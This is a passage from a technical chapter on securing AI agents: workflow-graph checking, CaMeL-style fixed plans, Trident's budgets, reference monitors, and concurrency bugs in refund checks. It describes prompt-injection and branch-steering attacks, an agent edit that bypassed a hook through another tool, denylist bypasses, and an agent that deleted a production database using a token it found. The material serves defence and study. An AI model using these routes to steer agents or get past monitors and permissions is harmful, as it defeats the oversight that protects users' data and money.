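Typed tools require evidence for each call, but the agent still chooses which calls to make. A workflow graph removes most of that choice. Before the agent starts, a developer lays out the steps, their order and the data that passes between them, so software can check every route for mistakes in advance. Workflow graphs suit work that follows the same pattern each time, but they work much less well for a request like "deal with whatever this email asks for", because nobody can lay out the steps before reading the email.

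### A graph for refunds

*Agentproof* (Xavier, Jolly and colleagues, 2026) defines a workflow graph as a set of nodes and edges with one entry and a set of exits. Each node has a kind, such as tool, language model, router or person, and a tool node lists the tools it calls. Each edge is direct, conditional, parallel or a loop. The definition omits data types, but a developer can add them from the tools' signatures.

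The shop's refund workflow could start from a form with the customer's email address, postcode, order number and message:

| Step | Done by | Takes | Returns | Next step |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Verify | tool | email address, postcode | `Customer` or `NoMatch` | Read, or End if there is no match |
| Read | tool | `Customer`, order number | `VerifiedOrder` or `NotFound` | Sort, or Write if there is no such order |
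| Sort | model | `VerifiedOrder`, message | `Amount` or `Question` | Approve for an amount, Write for a question |
| Approve | person | `VerifiedOrder`, `Amount` | `Approval` or `Refusal` | Refund, or Write after a refusal |
| Refund | tool | `VerifiedOrder`, `Amount`, `Approval` | `Refunded` or `Declined` | Write, or Approve again if the payment service declines |
| Write | model | message, results so far | `Text` | Send |
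| Send | tool | `Customer`, `Text` | `Sent` | End |

The graph branches wherever a row has two next steps, and it contains one loop, from Refund back to Approve.

### Checks before the first run

To check the types, software works out which values are available at each step s, whatever route the run takes:

```
available(s) = ⋂ over every edge p → s of
               ( available(p) ∪ values that p returns on that edge )
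```

A step passes if all its inputs are available on every route into it. Suppose that, to explain failures to the customer, a developer changes the graph so that a failed verification leads to Write instead of End. One route then reaches Send without a `Customer`, so the checker rejects the graph.

Two searches find the places where a run could get stuck. One follows the edges forwards from the entry, and the other follows them backwards from the exits. If only the forward search finds a step, a run can reach that step but can never finish from it. In an example from Xavier and colleagues, an agent sorts incoming email, and its developer adds a step that drafts replies to normal-priority messages but forgets to connect it to the sending step. Those drafts would go unsent without warning. Agentproof, their checker, prints the route from the entry to the dead end.

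To check that a person approves every refund, the software deletes the Approve step and searches forwards again. In the shop's graph, the search can no longer reach Refund, so every route to Refund goes through Approve. If a developer later adds an edge from Sort straight to Refund for amounts under £20, the search finds the route Verify, Read, Sort, Refund. The type check would also reject this edge, because Refund takes an `Approval`. Most existing payment tools don't take one, so the type check wouldn't catch the edge in a workflow that used them.

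However, the search can miss some mistakes. Suppose a declined refund leads straight back to Refund instead of to Approve. Deleting Approve still cuts Refund off from the entry, so the graph passes, even though one approval now covers any number of payment requests. To find this mistake, the software has to search pairs of a step and a rule state, which here records whether an unused approval exists. Approve creates an approval and Refund uses it up. The route Verify, Read, Sort, Approve, Refund, Refund reaches the second Refund without an unused approval, so the checker reports it. This second search covers at most |V| × |Q| pairs, where V is the set of steps and Q is the set of rule states.

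Agentproof does this with rules in a small temporal language. The rule `issue_refund -> F approve` means that an approval must come between one refund and the next. This form is easy to misuse. One example policy in *Agentproof*, labelled "Deploy approval", is `tool:deploy -> F tool:approve`. Under the language's definition, this rule allows the first deployment without approval and requires approval only before the second.

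Xavier and colleagues tested Agentproof on 18 small workflows that they wrote themselves, some with deliberate defects, so the test measures detection rather than how common defects are. Agentproof found structural defects in five of the workflows, and ten had no human step. The checks took about a tenth of a second on a graph of 5,000 nodes. In workflows built with LangGraph, a popular framework, Agentproof identifies a human step by the word "human" in its name, so it treats an approval step without that word in its name as a model step.

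### Graphs that only route and graphs that deny

Whether a checked graph constrains the agent depends on how the software uses it. Many applications use the graph only for routing, which means starting the next step when one finishes. A model step can contain an agent with its own tools, and routing does not stop that agent from using them.

Suppose the shop's developer reuses the support agent, with all four of its tools, for the Write step. The graph still shows an approval on every route to Refund, but the agent inside Write can call `issue_refund` directly. Agentproof would not report this, because its model of a workflow lists tools only for tool nodes.

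A graph enforces order only if a reference monitor stores the run's current step and denies every call that doesn't belong to it, as in *Soteria*'s strict mode. In the Write step, the monitor denies all tool calls. The graph also has to stay the same during the run. Some frameworks let code add agents or transitions while the workflow is running, and Xavier and colleagues note that the earlier checks then no longer apply unless the software repeats them on the new graph.

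### A program written before the data arrives

A developer can draw a graph by hand for refunds, which a shop handles every day, but not for every request that a personal assistant might receive. CaMeL, which Google DeepMind introduced in 2025, has a language model write a new workflow for each request before the model could have read anything from an attacker.

CaMeL separates the choice and order of actions from the processing of untrusted data, as *Can CaMeLs Talk?* (2026) explains. Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues (2026), in *CaMeLoT*, describe how it works:

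1. A privileged model receives the user's request and writes a program in a restricted form of Python.
2. An interpreter runs the program and makes the tool calls.
3. When the program needs to extract something from a text, the interpreter passes the text to a quarantined model. This model has no tools and can only return a value.
4. The interpreter labels each value with its sources and with the people who may read it. Before each tool call, a policy written as a Python function checks the arguments and their labels.

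Suppose an employee of the shop asks such an assistant to send a summary of order 1042 to ana@example.com. The privileged model might write:

```
order   = read_order(1042)
summary = ask_quarantined("Summarise this order", order)
send_email("ana@example.com", summary)
```

The planted sentence in the delivery note reaches only the quarantined model. It can make the summary false, but it can't add a second email or change the recipient, because the program was already written. The policy for `send_email` could require that the address come from the employee and that the address's owner be allowed to read the text. Both conditions hold, so the email would go out.

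Now suppose the employee asks the assistant to email the summary to the courier's address in the delivery note. The program has to extract the address with the quarantined model, so the label marks it as untrusted. The policy blocks the email, even though the employee asked for it and the address may be genuine.

CaMeLoT, a system by Nikolaou and colleagues, adds a check before the program runs. It converts the program into a finite-state machine and uses a model checker to search all the machine's runs for one that breaks a temporal-logic rule. If it finds one, the privileged model gets a description of that run and tries to repair the program. No tool has run at this point, so a bad program can be repaired before it does any harm.

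CaMeLoT can also check rules that a call-by-call monitor can't enforce, such as the rule that an email must eventually follow every refund. A finished program shows every possible next step, so the checker can reject a program if any route through it ends without the email. However, this proves only that each route contains the call to send the email, and the mail service could still fail.

In one test, a user told the agent to skip the required approval and disconnect a possibly compromised computer from the network. CaMeLoT rejected the resulting program, while a simplified version of CaMeL's checks allowed it. CaMeLoT also caught all seven unsafe programs that the researchers had written by hand, while the simplified version caught one. This was expected, because the researchers had chosen ordering rules that CaMeL's checks on single calls can't express.

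They also ran CaMeL and CaMeLoT on AgentDojo's 97 tasks, which cover banking, travel, office work and Slack, but left out the prompt injections. With Claude Haiku 4.5, CaMeL completed 49 tasks. Both systems blocked 17 tasks. In another 22, the program ran under both systems but didn't do what the user wanted. CaMeLoT could check 22 of CaMeL's 28 tool policies in advance. The other six depend on facts known only during the run, such as who can currently read a file.

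### Attackers who choose the branch

A program can allow for several possible results by branching on them. Suppose the shop's assistant wrote this for a complaint about order 1042:

```
damaged = ask_quarantined("Did the item arrive damaged?", message)
if damaged: issue_refund(1042, £60)
else:       send_email("ana@example.com", "Could you send us a photo?")
```

Whoever wrote the message decides which branch runs. Both branches are in the approved program, so the attacker doesn't need to inject an instruction. *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* (Foerster, Blanchard and colleagues, 2026) calls this branch steering. The paper adapts CaMeL to agents that control a computer through its screen, where the program must prepare for every window and pop-up that might appear. In one attack, an advertisement imitates a cookie notice. The program contains a step for closing cookie notices, so the agent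 clicks the advertisement and lands on the attacker's site.

Such programs also get long. On AgentDojo, CaMeL programs averaged 4.9 tool calls and 3.7 branches, while the computer-control programs averaged 41.1 calls and 39.7 branches. About half of their steps were fallbacks that a given run never used. On OSWorld, a benchmark of computer tasks, the agents retained at most 57 percent of the performance of leading models that could look at the screen before each action.

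*Securing Computer-Use Agents Against Branch Steering Attacks* (Zingrillo, Foerster and colleagues, 2026) introduces a benchmark of 101 tasks to measure branch steering. Across 74 attack configurations, the attacker succeeded in 90.5 percent of runs against an ordinary agent and 87.8 percent against the adapted version of CaMeL. The adapted version omits CaMeL's data-flow policies, so the 87.8 percent figure applies only to the fixed program.

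Their defence, COBRA, gives each branch its own limits on websites, tools and arguments before the agent reads any untrusted data. The effect of a mouse click can't be determined from the click alone, so COBRA checks the web request or tool call that results. None of the attacks succeeded against COBRA, and it kept 97 percent of the utility on tasks without an attack.

COBRA doesn't verify that a branch's condition is true, and it doesn't count repeated operations. In the shop, it could limit the refund branch to £60 on order 1042, but a customer who lied about the damage would still be paid. If the planner detects that the user's permission depends on a fact that only untrusted data can supply, COBRA prompts the user about it before the run starts.

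### Tasks whose steps are in the data

The main objection to fixed plans is that many useful requests don't say what to do. Costa, Köpf and colleagues (2025), in *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control*, make this precise. Let D be the set of possible states of the data, and let solutions(d) be the set of sequences of tool calls, each with a final answer, that complete the task when the data is d. A task is data-independent if

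```
⋂ over all d in D of solutions(d) ≠ ∅
```

A task is data-independent if the same sequence of actions completes it whatever the data contains. "Send my three latest emails to Ben" is data-independent, because the agent can forward the emails without reading them. "Complete the tasks due today in my to-do app" is data-dependent, because the agent has to read the tasks to know which actions to take. A branching program can handle a data-dependent task if the program's author can foresee the cases, but no author can foresee everything a to-do list might contain.

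Costa and colleagues classify only 20 of AgentDojo's 97 tasks as data-dependent, so a system that can't change its plan can still do well on the benchmark. *AgentDyn* (2026) tests whether defences remain usable on more open-ended tasks, and describes its own attacks as relatively weak against the latest models.

Costa and colleagues' system, FIDES, lets the planner model choose one tool call at a time. When a tool returns untrusted text, FIDES stores it in a variable and gives the planner only the variable's name. The planner can pass the variable to another tool or have a quarantined model answer a question about the text. If the answer can only be yes or no, it carries at most one bit, and a policy may allow the planner to act on it. If the planner reads the full text, everything it does afterwards counts as untrusted, and the policy blocks consequential actions.

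With suitable policies, FIDES stopped every AgentDojo attack in the paper's tests. It also completed more tasks than a basic planner under policy enforcement, 8 percent more with GPT-4o and 16 percent more with o1. But FIDES doesn't track how much information these answers reveal in total, so the planner could learn a lot from many small ones.

Progent takes a different approach and changes the permissions during the run. Shi, He and colleagues (2025), in *Progent*, describe a user who asks an agent to carry out the to-do list in an email from Alice. At first, the policy permits only a search for that email. The list asks for a summary of recent emails on Slack, so a language model proposes rules for reading email and posting to Slack. A solver then compares the new policy P′ with the old policy P. If A(P) is the set of calls that P permits, the software applies the update automatically when

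```
A(P′) ⊆ A(P)
```

In Progent, any policy update that would permit something new needs approval. On AgentDojo, 6 percent of updates did. With GPT-4o, the initial policy alone cut the attack success rate from 39.9 to 2.5 percent, and adding updates cut it to 1.0 percent, even though the test approved all of them. The model that proposes the updates is the weak point, because it reads the results of tool calls, including any planted text. The solver can detect that a new rule permits more, but it cannot determine whether the user would want that.

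### Trident's three models

*Trident* (November 2026) lets untrusted data influence the plan but limits how much information the planner can get from it. In its example, an employee's manager, Jane, has forwarded a caterer's email about a team event. The employee asks the agent to handle the email's requests, pay from the team account and let Jane know. The email contains an invoice and several requests, so nobody can write the full plan until the agent has read it.

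Trident divides the work among three language models:

- The planner chooses tool calls but never reads untrusted text.
- The data model reads untrusted text but has no tools. It answers the planner's questions in a fixed format.
- The policy model writes the rules from the user's request, the administrator's policy and the tool descriptions. It never receives tool results or the planner's proposals, so text in the email can't lead it to widen the rules, as can happen in Progent.

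A reference monitor made of ordinary code checks every output of all three. Its policies are state machines with guards and registers, like the shop's, and they are nested:

| Policy | Author | What it permits in the example |
|---|---|---|
| Root policy | Administrator, before deployment | Emails to colleagues and to vendors on file, and payments of up to $5,000 to three vendors on file |
| Task ceiling | Policy model, from the request | One payment, and replies to Jane and one vendor contact |
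| Task policy at the start | Policy model, from the request | Reading Jane's email and replying to her |

At the start, the task policy permits no payment because the agent doesn't yet know whom to pay. The policy model can handle this by selecting a template, a rule with a blank that the monitor fills in later. The administrator's payment template permits one payment of up to $5,000 to an account θ if θ comes from a vendor record on file.

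Before the run, the monitor uses a solver to check that the policies fit inside one another. Let A(P) again be the set of calls that policy P permits at some point, and L(P) the set of sequences it permits. For every template R and every permitted value of θ, the checks are:

```
A(task) ⊆ A(ceiling) ⊆ A(root)
L(task) ⊆ L(ceiling) ⊆ L(root)
A(R(θ)) ⊆ A(ceiling)
```

The check on sequences is necessary because two policies can permit the same calls in different orders.

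The planner then processes the email without reading it. It queries the data model to find out whether there is an invoice and which of the three vendors sent it. It also requests the amount and a draft reply, but the monitor keeps these sealed and gives the planner only labels for them. The agent looks up the vendor, and the monitor copies the account number from the vendor's record into the template. The task policy now permits one payment to that account.

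If the email says "our bank details have changed", the new account number comes from untrusted text, so the root policy denies a payment to it. The attacker can still influence the amount, because no trusted record contains it. A false invoice could cause an overpayment of up to $5,000, but the money would go to a vendor on file.

If a call passes the root policy but no rule for the task permits it, the monitor approves it when all its inputs are trusted. Otherwise, the monitor shows the exact call to the user, who can approve it once. The user can't approve a call that breaks the root policy.

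### What the two theorems guarantee

Each answer the planner receives uses part of an influence budget β. An answer with n possible values uses log₂ n bits, so a yes-or-no answer uses one bit and a choice among three vendors uses about 1.58. Telling the planner whether a query or call succeeded uses one bit of a separate feedback budget σ if untrusted data could affect the result. Sealed values don't use either budget.

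The researchers proved two theorems and checked the proofs by computer. The first concerns what the agent can do. Let Pₜ be the task policy at step t, Enabled(Pₜ) the calls it permits at that moment, and Eₜ all the calls covered by the rules written so far, including templates still waiting for a value. Then at every step

```
Enabled(Pₜ) ⊆ Eₜ ⊆ A(root)    and at the start    E₀ ⊆ A(ceiling)
```

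Every call must pass the root policy to run. It must also pass the ceiling and the task policy, unless the user or the monitor has approved that exact call. The user can confirm a new rule during the task, and calls under that rule don't have to pass the ceiling.

The second theorem concerns how far an attacker can steer the plan. It holds the trusted inputs, the models' random choices and the user's decisions fixed, and varies only the untrusted data. The number of different observable traces is then at most

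```
⌊2^(β + σ)⌋
```

An observable trace consists of the planner's proposals, the monitor's replies and the calls that ran, but not the contents of sealed values. The proof treats the run as a tree that branches whenever the planner receives an answer. An answer with n possible values creates n branches and uses at least log₂ n bits of budget, so a tree with a total budget of B bits has at most 2ᴮ ends. If both budgets are zero, an attacker can't change the trace.

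The theorems don't depend on the models behaving well, but they do rest on five assumptions:

- Each model receives only the inputs that the design gives it, and every tool call passes through the monitor.
- The tool descriptions correctly state what each tool reads, changes and depends on.
- The monitor's storage carries those dependencies over to every value derived from untrusted data.
- The root policy stays fixed, the solver makes no mistakes, and the user and the approval screen are trustworthy.
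- Calls run one at a time, and every permitted call finishes successfully and returns a result.

A payment whose reply gets lost breaks the last assumption, so the theorems don't cover the shop's double refund.

The bound on traces can also be very loose. In tests on data-dependent tasks, the median run used 19 to 26 bits of influence and 5 to 10 bits of feedback, depending on the model. Even the lowest of these figures total 24 bits, and budgets of that size would let an attacker choose among 2²⁴, or about 16.8 million, traces. The root policy restricts all of these traces, which matters more for safety than their number. But a single bit can do harm if it decides between two permitted payments. *Trident* acknowledges that its budgets don't prevent branch steering.

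### Results on AgentDojo and ReplanInject

The researchers compared Trident with an undefended agent, CaMeL, Progent and FIDES. They tested FIDES both as its paper describes it and with a later option that asks the user to approve blocked calls. They report attack success once assuming that the user grants every request, and once assuming that the user rejects every request that shows the attacker's call. A real user would fall between the two.

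These are the AgentDojo results with GPT-4.1, based on 97 ordinary runs and 909 attacked ones:

| Defence | Utility, no attack | Utility under attack | Attack success, all requests granted | Attack success, careful review | Cost per run |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| None | 82.5% | 56.9% | 34.1% | never asks | $0.012 |
| CaMeL | 42.3% | 46.4% | 0.0% | never asks | $0.034 |
| Progent | 76.3% | 64.0% | 4.6% | 1.4% | $0.028 |
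| FIDES | 25.8% | 26.8% | 0.1% | never asks | $0.025 |
| FIDES with approvals | 50.5% | 46.0% | 3.1% | 0.7% | $0.026 |
| Trident | 68.0% | 64.0% | 0.1% | 0.0% | $0.119 |

Trident completed as many attacked tasks as Progent and let fewer attacks through, but it cost about four times as much.

AgentDojo has few data-dependent tasks, so the researchers also built ReplanInject, a benchmark of 45 tasks. In two of them, the request names every action. In 22, the untrusted content settles a condition or a choice, such as whether a venue has confirmed a booking. In 18, it determines which actions to take, and in the last three the request says only where to look. The attacker's text is always inside content that the agent has to read. These are the results with GPT-4.1, averaged over three repetitions:

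| Defence | Utility under attack | Attack success, all requests granted | Attack success, careful review | Requests per attacked run |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| None | 20.2% | 68.1% | never asks | 0 |
| CaMeL | 9.8% | 0.0% | never asks | 0 |
| Progent | 35.4% | 33.1% | 11.9% | 2.09 |
| FIDES | 5.1% | 0.1% | never asks | 0 |
| FIDES with approvals | 36.6% | 6.5% | 0.0% | 1.19 |
| Trident | 54.2% | 4.1% | 0.0% | 0.91 |

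Without an attack, the undefended agent completed about 86 percent of the tasks, Trident 60.7 percent, CaMeL 7.4 percent and FIDES without approvals 4.4 percent. CaMeL's low score supports the objection to fixed plans. In 574 of its 1,215 runs with GPT-4.1, its policy denied a call because the call depended on untrusted data, even though it contained nothing from the attacker. In another 377 runs, the quarantined model failed to extract what the program needed.

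Trident's cost per ReplanInject run ranged from $0.10 to $0.24 across four models, compared with $0.005 to $0.045 for the undefended agent. Its lead in utility also depends on the model. On Claude Sonnet 4.5, Trident completed 64.4 percent of attacked runs, while FIDES with approvals completed 75.2 percent. However, FIDES asked the user more often and let more attacks through when the user granted every request.

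Trident only partly solves the problem it was designed for. On the 18 tasks where the content determines the actions, it completed 22.0 to 41.4 percent of attacked runs. The researchers read 48 failed runs and found that sealing the text caused only one of the failures. In most of the others, the planner chose the wrong record, value or tool, or the data model gave a wrong answer. A more capable model might therefore do much better with the same design.

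The tests provide little evidence about the budgets, because the researchers set them too high to affect any run. The low attack success came from the sealed text, the policies and the user's review. The researchers later used the recorded runs to estimate the effect of capping each budget at 32 bits. With GPT-4.1, the cap would have lowered attack success from 4.1 to 3.1 percent and utility under attack from 54.2 to 49.0 percent. The handwritten root policies mattered less than one might expect, since with generic ones utility under attack was 52.5 percent and attack success was 5.8 percent.

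The researchers avoided the latest models because they needed attacks that work against an undefended agent. Even Sonnet 4.5 resisted every AgentDojo attack without any defence, so Trident could not improve its security on that benchmark. It only added overhead and lowered utility under attack from 86.8 to 82.4 percent. On ReplanInject, 12.9 percent of attacks on the undefended Sonnet 4.5 succeeded, so its resistance to AgentDojo's attacks did not carry over fully to tasks where the agent must follow untrusted content. How much protection Trident would add to a current model is unknown.

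### How often a person has to decide

Trident prompted the user for approval 0.91 to 1.25 times per attacked ReplanInject run, depending on the model, and about half as often on AgentDojo. Progent did so 1.17 to 3.29 times on ReplanInject. If the user had approved at most one call per run, Trident would have completed 48.1 to 59.2 percent of attacked runs, compared with 54.2 to 74.2 percent without the limit.

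Most of Trident's requests in attacked ReplanInject runs concerned the user's own task, and only 5.7 to 8.8 percent showed the attacker's call, so a user who habitually clicked "approve" would usually be right. The researchers estimate that attack success would stay at or below 0.6 percent if the user wrongly approved one in ten of the requests that showed the attacker's call, assuming that an attack can't make the user more careless. The strongest attack designed specifically against Trident used text disguised as a correction to a payment the user expected to approve, and it succeeded in 10.0 percent of runs when the user granted every request.

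Attacks on Progent still succeeded 5.8 to 11.9 percent of the time on ReplanInject, even with careful review. Progent users approve changes to the policy, and a change can permit the attacker's call without showing them that call. Trident users see the call itself and its arguments, with a label on each argument that came from untrusted text.

This still leaves the user with a hard decision when the task is as open as "do what Jane's email says". On the three tasks of this kind, 13.9 to 27.8 percent of attacks succeeded when the user granted every request. The attacker's instruction looks like the ones the user asked the agent to follow, so the user may have to ask Jane which instructions she wrote.

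## How harmful actions get past the check

A monitor can apply a correct rule accurately and still fail to prevent harm. It protects the shop only if the rules forbid the harmful actions, every such action passes through the monitor, the monitor can determine what a proposed call will do, and the facts it relies on are still true when the call takes effect.

### An edit that skipped the check

Saltzer and Schroeder's principle of complete mediation requires a system to check every access to every object. This is hard to achieve with agents because they often have several tools that can do the same thing. Markus Eisele describes a harmless example from October 2026 in DZone's *AI Coding Agent Guardrails*. He asked IBM's coding agent Bob to change a small web application and wanted to keep the agent away from the configuration file. A hook, a small program that runs before a tool and can block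 it, was supposed to permit edits only in two source folders. The agent made the requested changes and the test passed, but neither edit went through the hook because Eisele had attached it to the tool `write_file` and the agent used `apply_diff`.

Both edits were in permitted folders, so the hook should have allowed them anyway. But it would also have missed a forbidden edit made with `apply_diff`, and a test that looked only at what the agent did would not have revealed this. Zhou and Zhang (2026), in *Rethinking Access Control for AI Agents*, therefore argue that evaluations should also look for unauthorised effects that remain possible. Let E be all the effects that the deployed controls allow, α a function that describes those effects in the policy's terms, and ⟦P⟧ the effects that policy P permits. The controls preserve the policy's restrictions only if

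```
α(E) ⊆ ⟦P⟧
```

Eisele's hook failed this condition even though the agent broke no rule.

Eisele then extended the hook to four editing tools, including `apply_diff`. It still doesn't cover shell commands, which can also change files, or any editing tool that IBM adds later. Covering only `write_file` is an easy mistake to make, since the example of a blocking hook in IBM's *Lifecycle hooks* does the same. According to that documentation, a hook that names no tool runs before all of them. Such a hook could refuse every tool it doesn't recognise, which would follow the principle of fail-safe defaults. Lambert (2026), in *Ensuring proper AI security controls*, describes a personal assistant that applies this principle. Its software treats every tool as able to change data unless the tool's description marks it as read-only, so a new tool requires the user's approval by default.

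Bob's hooks may also let an edit through unchecked if they crash. A hook can block a tool by exiting with code 2, but Bob logs any other error code and carries on.

The file system is a better place for this check. If the operating system gives the agent's process read-only access to the configuration file, and the agent can't change that permission, then none of its editing tools or shell commands can alter the file.

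An action can also run before the check does. *The Balkanization of Execution-Security Research for AI Coding Agents* (Rashidi, 2026) lists a flaw in Claude Code that Anthropic has since fixed. Versions before 1.0.111 could run code from an untrusted project before the user accepted the trust dialog.

### The database deletion

In April 2026, Cursor, a coding agent running Claude Opus 4.6, deleted the production database of PocketOS, which makes software for car rental businesses. Founder Jer Crane, quoted by PC Gamer, said the agent was doing a routine task in the staging (test) environment when it hit a credential problem. It tried to fix this by deleting a storage volume with one call to the cloud provider, Railway. The call took nine seconds and, according to Computing's *AI coding agent goes rogue, deletes company database in nine seconds*, caused a 30-hour outage.

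Abdelwahab gives Railway's own account in *Your AI wants to nuke your database. Guardrails fix that*. The agent found an access token on the user's machine and sent the deletion request straight to Railway's API, the interface that other programs use. The token gave access to the whole account. Railway's dashboard delayed deletions by 48 hours so that customers could undo them, but the API deleted volumes immediately. Crane reported that the backups were gone too, but Abdelwahab writes that they only looked unavailable and that Railway recovered all the data.

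A monitor that covered only a list of Railway tools would not have stopped this, because the agent sent an ordinary web request. Railway already offered tokens limited to one project or environment. A token limited to staging would have given the agent no authority over a production volume, so the API would have refused the request whichever tool the agent used.

A delay would have made the deletion reversible, though it would not have blocked the request. Railway (2026) announced on 1 May that API deletions now wait 48 hours, as dashboard deletions already did. The difference between the two had been deliberate, or at least documented. In *Postgress volume lost*, a Railway support forum thread about another volume deleted in April, an employee quoted the API documentation, which described such deletions as permanent.

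Lambert argues that approval enforced by software would have prevented the deletion, but this is true only if the approval covers every tool that can send a web request. Lambert's tools all come from one server, whereas a coding agent with a shell can send requests in many other ways. Abdelwahab recommends Railway's newer server for agents, which offers a fixed set of tools and leaves no tokens on disk. This protects a customer only if the agent can't find an old token.

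### Tools that can do almost anything

A state machine that checks only tool names treats all shell commands as the same action, so a rule that permits a shell tool permits every program the shell can start. *Constraining AI agents with Red Hat AI* (Ableidinger, 2026) explains that an agent on a laptop typically inherits whatever its user can access, including files, the network and credentials in memory. This can lead to serious harm even without an attacker. Tom's Hardware's *Claude Opus 5 mistakenly deletes dev's entire profile directory during routine backup* reports that the model had mistaken the user's home directory for a temporary backup.

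Some developers filter the text of commands with a denylist, a list of forbidden patterns. Rashidi describes a test of 1,709 such lists from GitHub. A program called ShellSieve used a language model to generate possible bypasses, then ran them in a sandbox to check whether they worked. Depending on the type of bypass, 69.0 to 98.6 percent of the lists were vulnerable.

Filters fail because they examine the text of a command, while its effect depends on how the shell interprets that text and which programs the command starts. Many commands can delete the same file. The command that runs the tests can also change its effect without changing its text, because it executes whatever the tests contain, and a coding agent can usually edit them. Statewright's testing phase, which allows shell commands only for running tests, therefore restricts the agent less than it seems to.

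A sandbox restricts what commands can do instead of how they are written. The operating system gives the agent's process access to only certain folders and network addresses, and these limits apply to every command it runs. An agent in a sandbox that contained only a project folder could not delete the user's home directory or find a token stored elsewhere on the machine.

A sandbox doesn't check requests to a service that the agent is allowed to contact. If the agent needs Railway's API for its work, a network rule that lets it create a volume may also let it delete one. Narrow credentials help, but they often can't express the whole policy. In an example from Zhou and Zhang, a user permits an agent to send one summary to Alice, but the system issues a credential for sending mail in general. The mail service correctly accepts the credential, and would also deliver the summary if the agent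 addressed it to Bob.

The shop can avoid this by keeping the payment service's credential in the monitor, where the agent can't access it. The agent then has to send each refund request to the monitor, which checks it against the full policy before using the credential. This also helps with complete mediation, because a request that bypasses the monitor has no valid credential.

Sandboxes can also have flaws. Rashidi cites a 2024 vulnerability in widely used container software that let a program escape to the host's files, and a benchmark in which capable models found and exploited known types of weakness. The shop therefore still needs the check, with the sandbox as a second barrier that limits the damage when the check fails.

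### Two refunds that both pass

A monitor that checks every call can still decide on outdated facts. Suppose Ana asks for the same refund by chat and by email, and two agents handle the requests at the same time. Each has its own monitor, and both monitors read a shared database field called `refunded`:

| Step | Agent A's monitor | Agent B's monitor | `refunded` | Total paid |
|---|---|---|---|---|
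| 1 | reads "no" | | no | £0 |
| 2 | | reads "no" | no | £0 |
| 3 | permits the refund, pays £60 | | no | £60 |
| 4 | | permits the refund, pays £60 | no | £120 |
| 5 | writes "yes" | writes "yes" | yes | £120 |

Each monitor applied the rule correctly to the value it read. The field ends up the same as it would after a single refund, so it doesn't reveal the mistake. Writing "yes" before paying protects a single monitor against a lost reply, but it doesn't help here because both monitors read the field before either changes it.

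The repair is to make the check and the change one atomic operation, meaning that no other operation can come between them. The shop replaces the yes-or-no field with a status:

```
UPDATE orders
SET    refund = 'reserved', request = 'R1'
WHERE  id = 1042 AND refund = 'none'
```

The database reports how many rows it changed, and a monitor may pay only if the answer is one:

| Step | Agent A's monitor | Agent B's monitor | `refund` | Total paid |
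|---|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | changes one row | | reserved | £0 |
| 2 | | changes no rows, denies the refund | reserved | £0 |
| 3 | pays £60 | | reserved | £60 |
| 4 | writes "refunded" | | refunded | £60 |

If both updates arrive at once, the database makes one wait for the other. Programmers call this a compare-and-swap. *AID-Guard* (2026) uses the same two stages for agents. It reserves one unit of a quota when it grants a permission. When the agent uses the permission, a compare-and-swap on the server changes the reservation to "in flight". For partial refunds, the shop can keep a running total and add x only if the new total is at most the price.

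Two actions can conflict even if they change different records. *Stateful Governance for Concurrent Agentic Systems* (Peng and Wu, 2026) describes a team that has spent 9 of its 10 credits for the day. Two agents each transfer one credit from different accounts, and both transfers pass the check, bringing the team's spending to 11. In a scripted test where the limit allowed only 50 of 256 transfers, uncoordinated checks let through about 80. Cedar, an established policy engine, produced a similar result when the application supplied the spending figure with each request. MasuGate, Peng and Wu's system, permitted exactly 50 because it protects the spending figure from the time of the check until the transfer is complete.

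A single lock on the whole system also gave the right result, but it makes unrelated requests wait for each other. MasuGate locks only the records a decision depends on. It still needs complete mediation, because an administrator's script that changed the budget directly could invalidate a decision.

### Retries and half-finished work

If the payment service doesn't reply, the order's status should stay "reserved". The monitor can then query the service about request R1 and record the answer. Zhou and Zhang recommend counting the amount as possibly spent until the monitor has an answer, so that no agent can use the money for something else.

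*Verified Tool Calls Improve LLM Agent Reliability Under Non-Atomic Failures* (Mansoor, Phadke and Rana, 2026) tested agents on simulated tools that sometimes timed out after the action had already taken effect. At the highest fault level, an agent told to retry immediately duplicated an action in 72 percent of runs on one task and 76 percent on another. The rate fell to 20 percent on both tasks when software first checked whether the action had happened and attached a key that let the tool recognise a repeated request. The comparison favours the software, because the researchers deliberately told the other agent not to check. The remaining duplicates matter more for the shop, because a check soon after a timeout can return old data that makes a payment look as if it never happened.

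Duplicate detection also depends on the choice of key. Mansoor and colleagues compute it from the agent's identity, the action, its arguments and the time period, so two agents refunding the same order would send different keys, as would one agent that changed the amount on its second attempt. Zhou and Zhang warn that agents may respond to a timeout by changing the arguments, splitting the request or switching tools. In the shop, the monitor should attach the reservation number, R1, as the key to every attempt to pay that refund, and the payment service has to support duplicate detection.

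Some tasks have several steps that should all succeed or all fail. *Atomix* (Mohammadi, Potamitis and colleagues, 2026) gives the example of an agent that books a flight, a hotel and a car, then emails a confirmation. If the flight booking fails, the software can cancel the hotel and the car, but it can't take back an email. Atomix therefore holds the email until the bookings are settled and tells the agent that it is queued, which avoids the false "sent" that an edit automaton might report. In a test, Atomix released all 500 valid emails and none of the 500 invalid ones. Holding emails this way depends on a developer correctly classifying email as irreversible.

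### Facts that change after the check

The two refunds are an example of a time-of-check to time-of-use gap, in which something changes between a check and the action that relies on it. In *Mind the Gap*, Lilienthal and Hong (2025) examined 66 AgentDojo tasks that need at least two tool calls. In 56 of them, a later call relied on information that could have changed since an earlier call read it. When they combined pairs of Slack tools into single tools, the average gap fell from 1.70 to 0.07 seconds. Some gap remains unless the service itself performs both steps atomically.

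When an action needs human approval, hours can pass between the check and the action. In Peng and Wu's example, a transfer fits the budget when a person receives the request, but another agent spends the money before the person answers. The software can either reserve the money while the person decides or repeat the check after the approval. Lambert's assistant accepts an approval only for the exact operation the user was shown, and only for ten minutes.

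*Temporary Authority, Permanent Effects* (2026) shows that checking each part of an action separately is not enough, because two different approvals may cover the parts. For example, if a manager approved £60 for one order and £20 for another, the check might accept £60 for the second order. The monitor has to find a single approval that covers the whole action and has not been replaced by a newer one.

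Tools can also change. Zhou and Zhang point out that a tool might start forwarding data to an outside service while keeping its name and arguments. A monitor that relied on the old description would still permit it. The operator should review a tool's permissions whenever its behaviour changes.

### Rules divided among several agents

When an agent delegates work, the agents' separate limits can add up to more than the user allowed, as in Sterling's shared-budget example. An atomic reservation also solves this if all the agents draw on the same limit.

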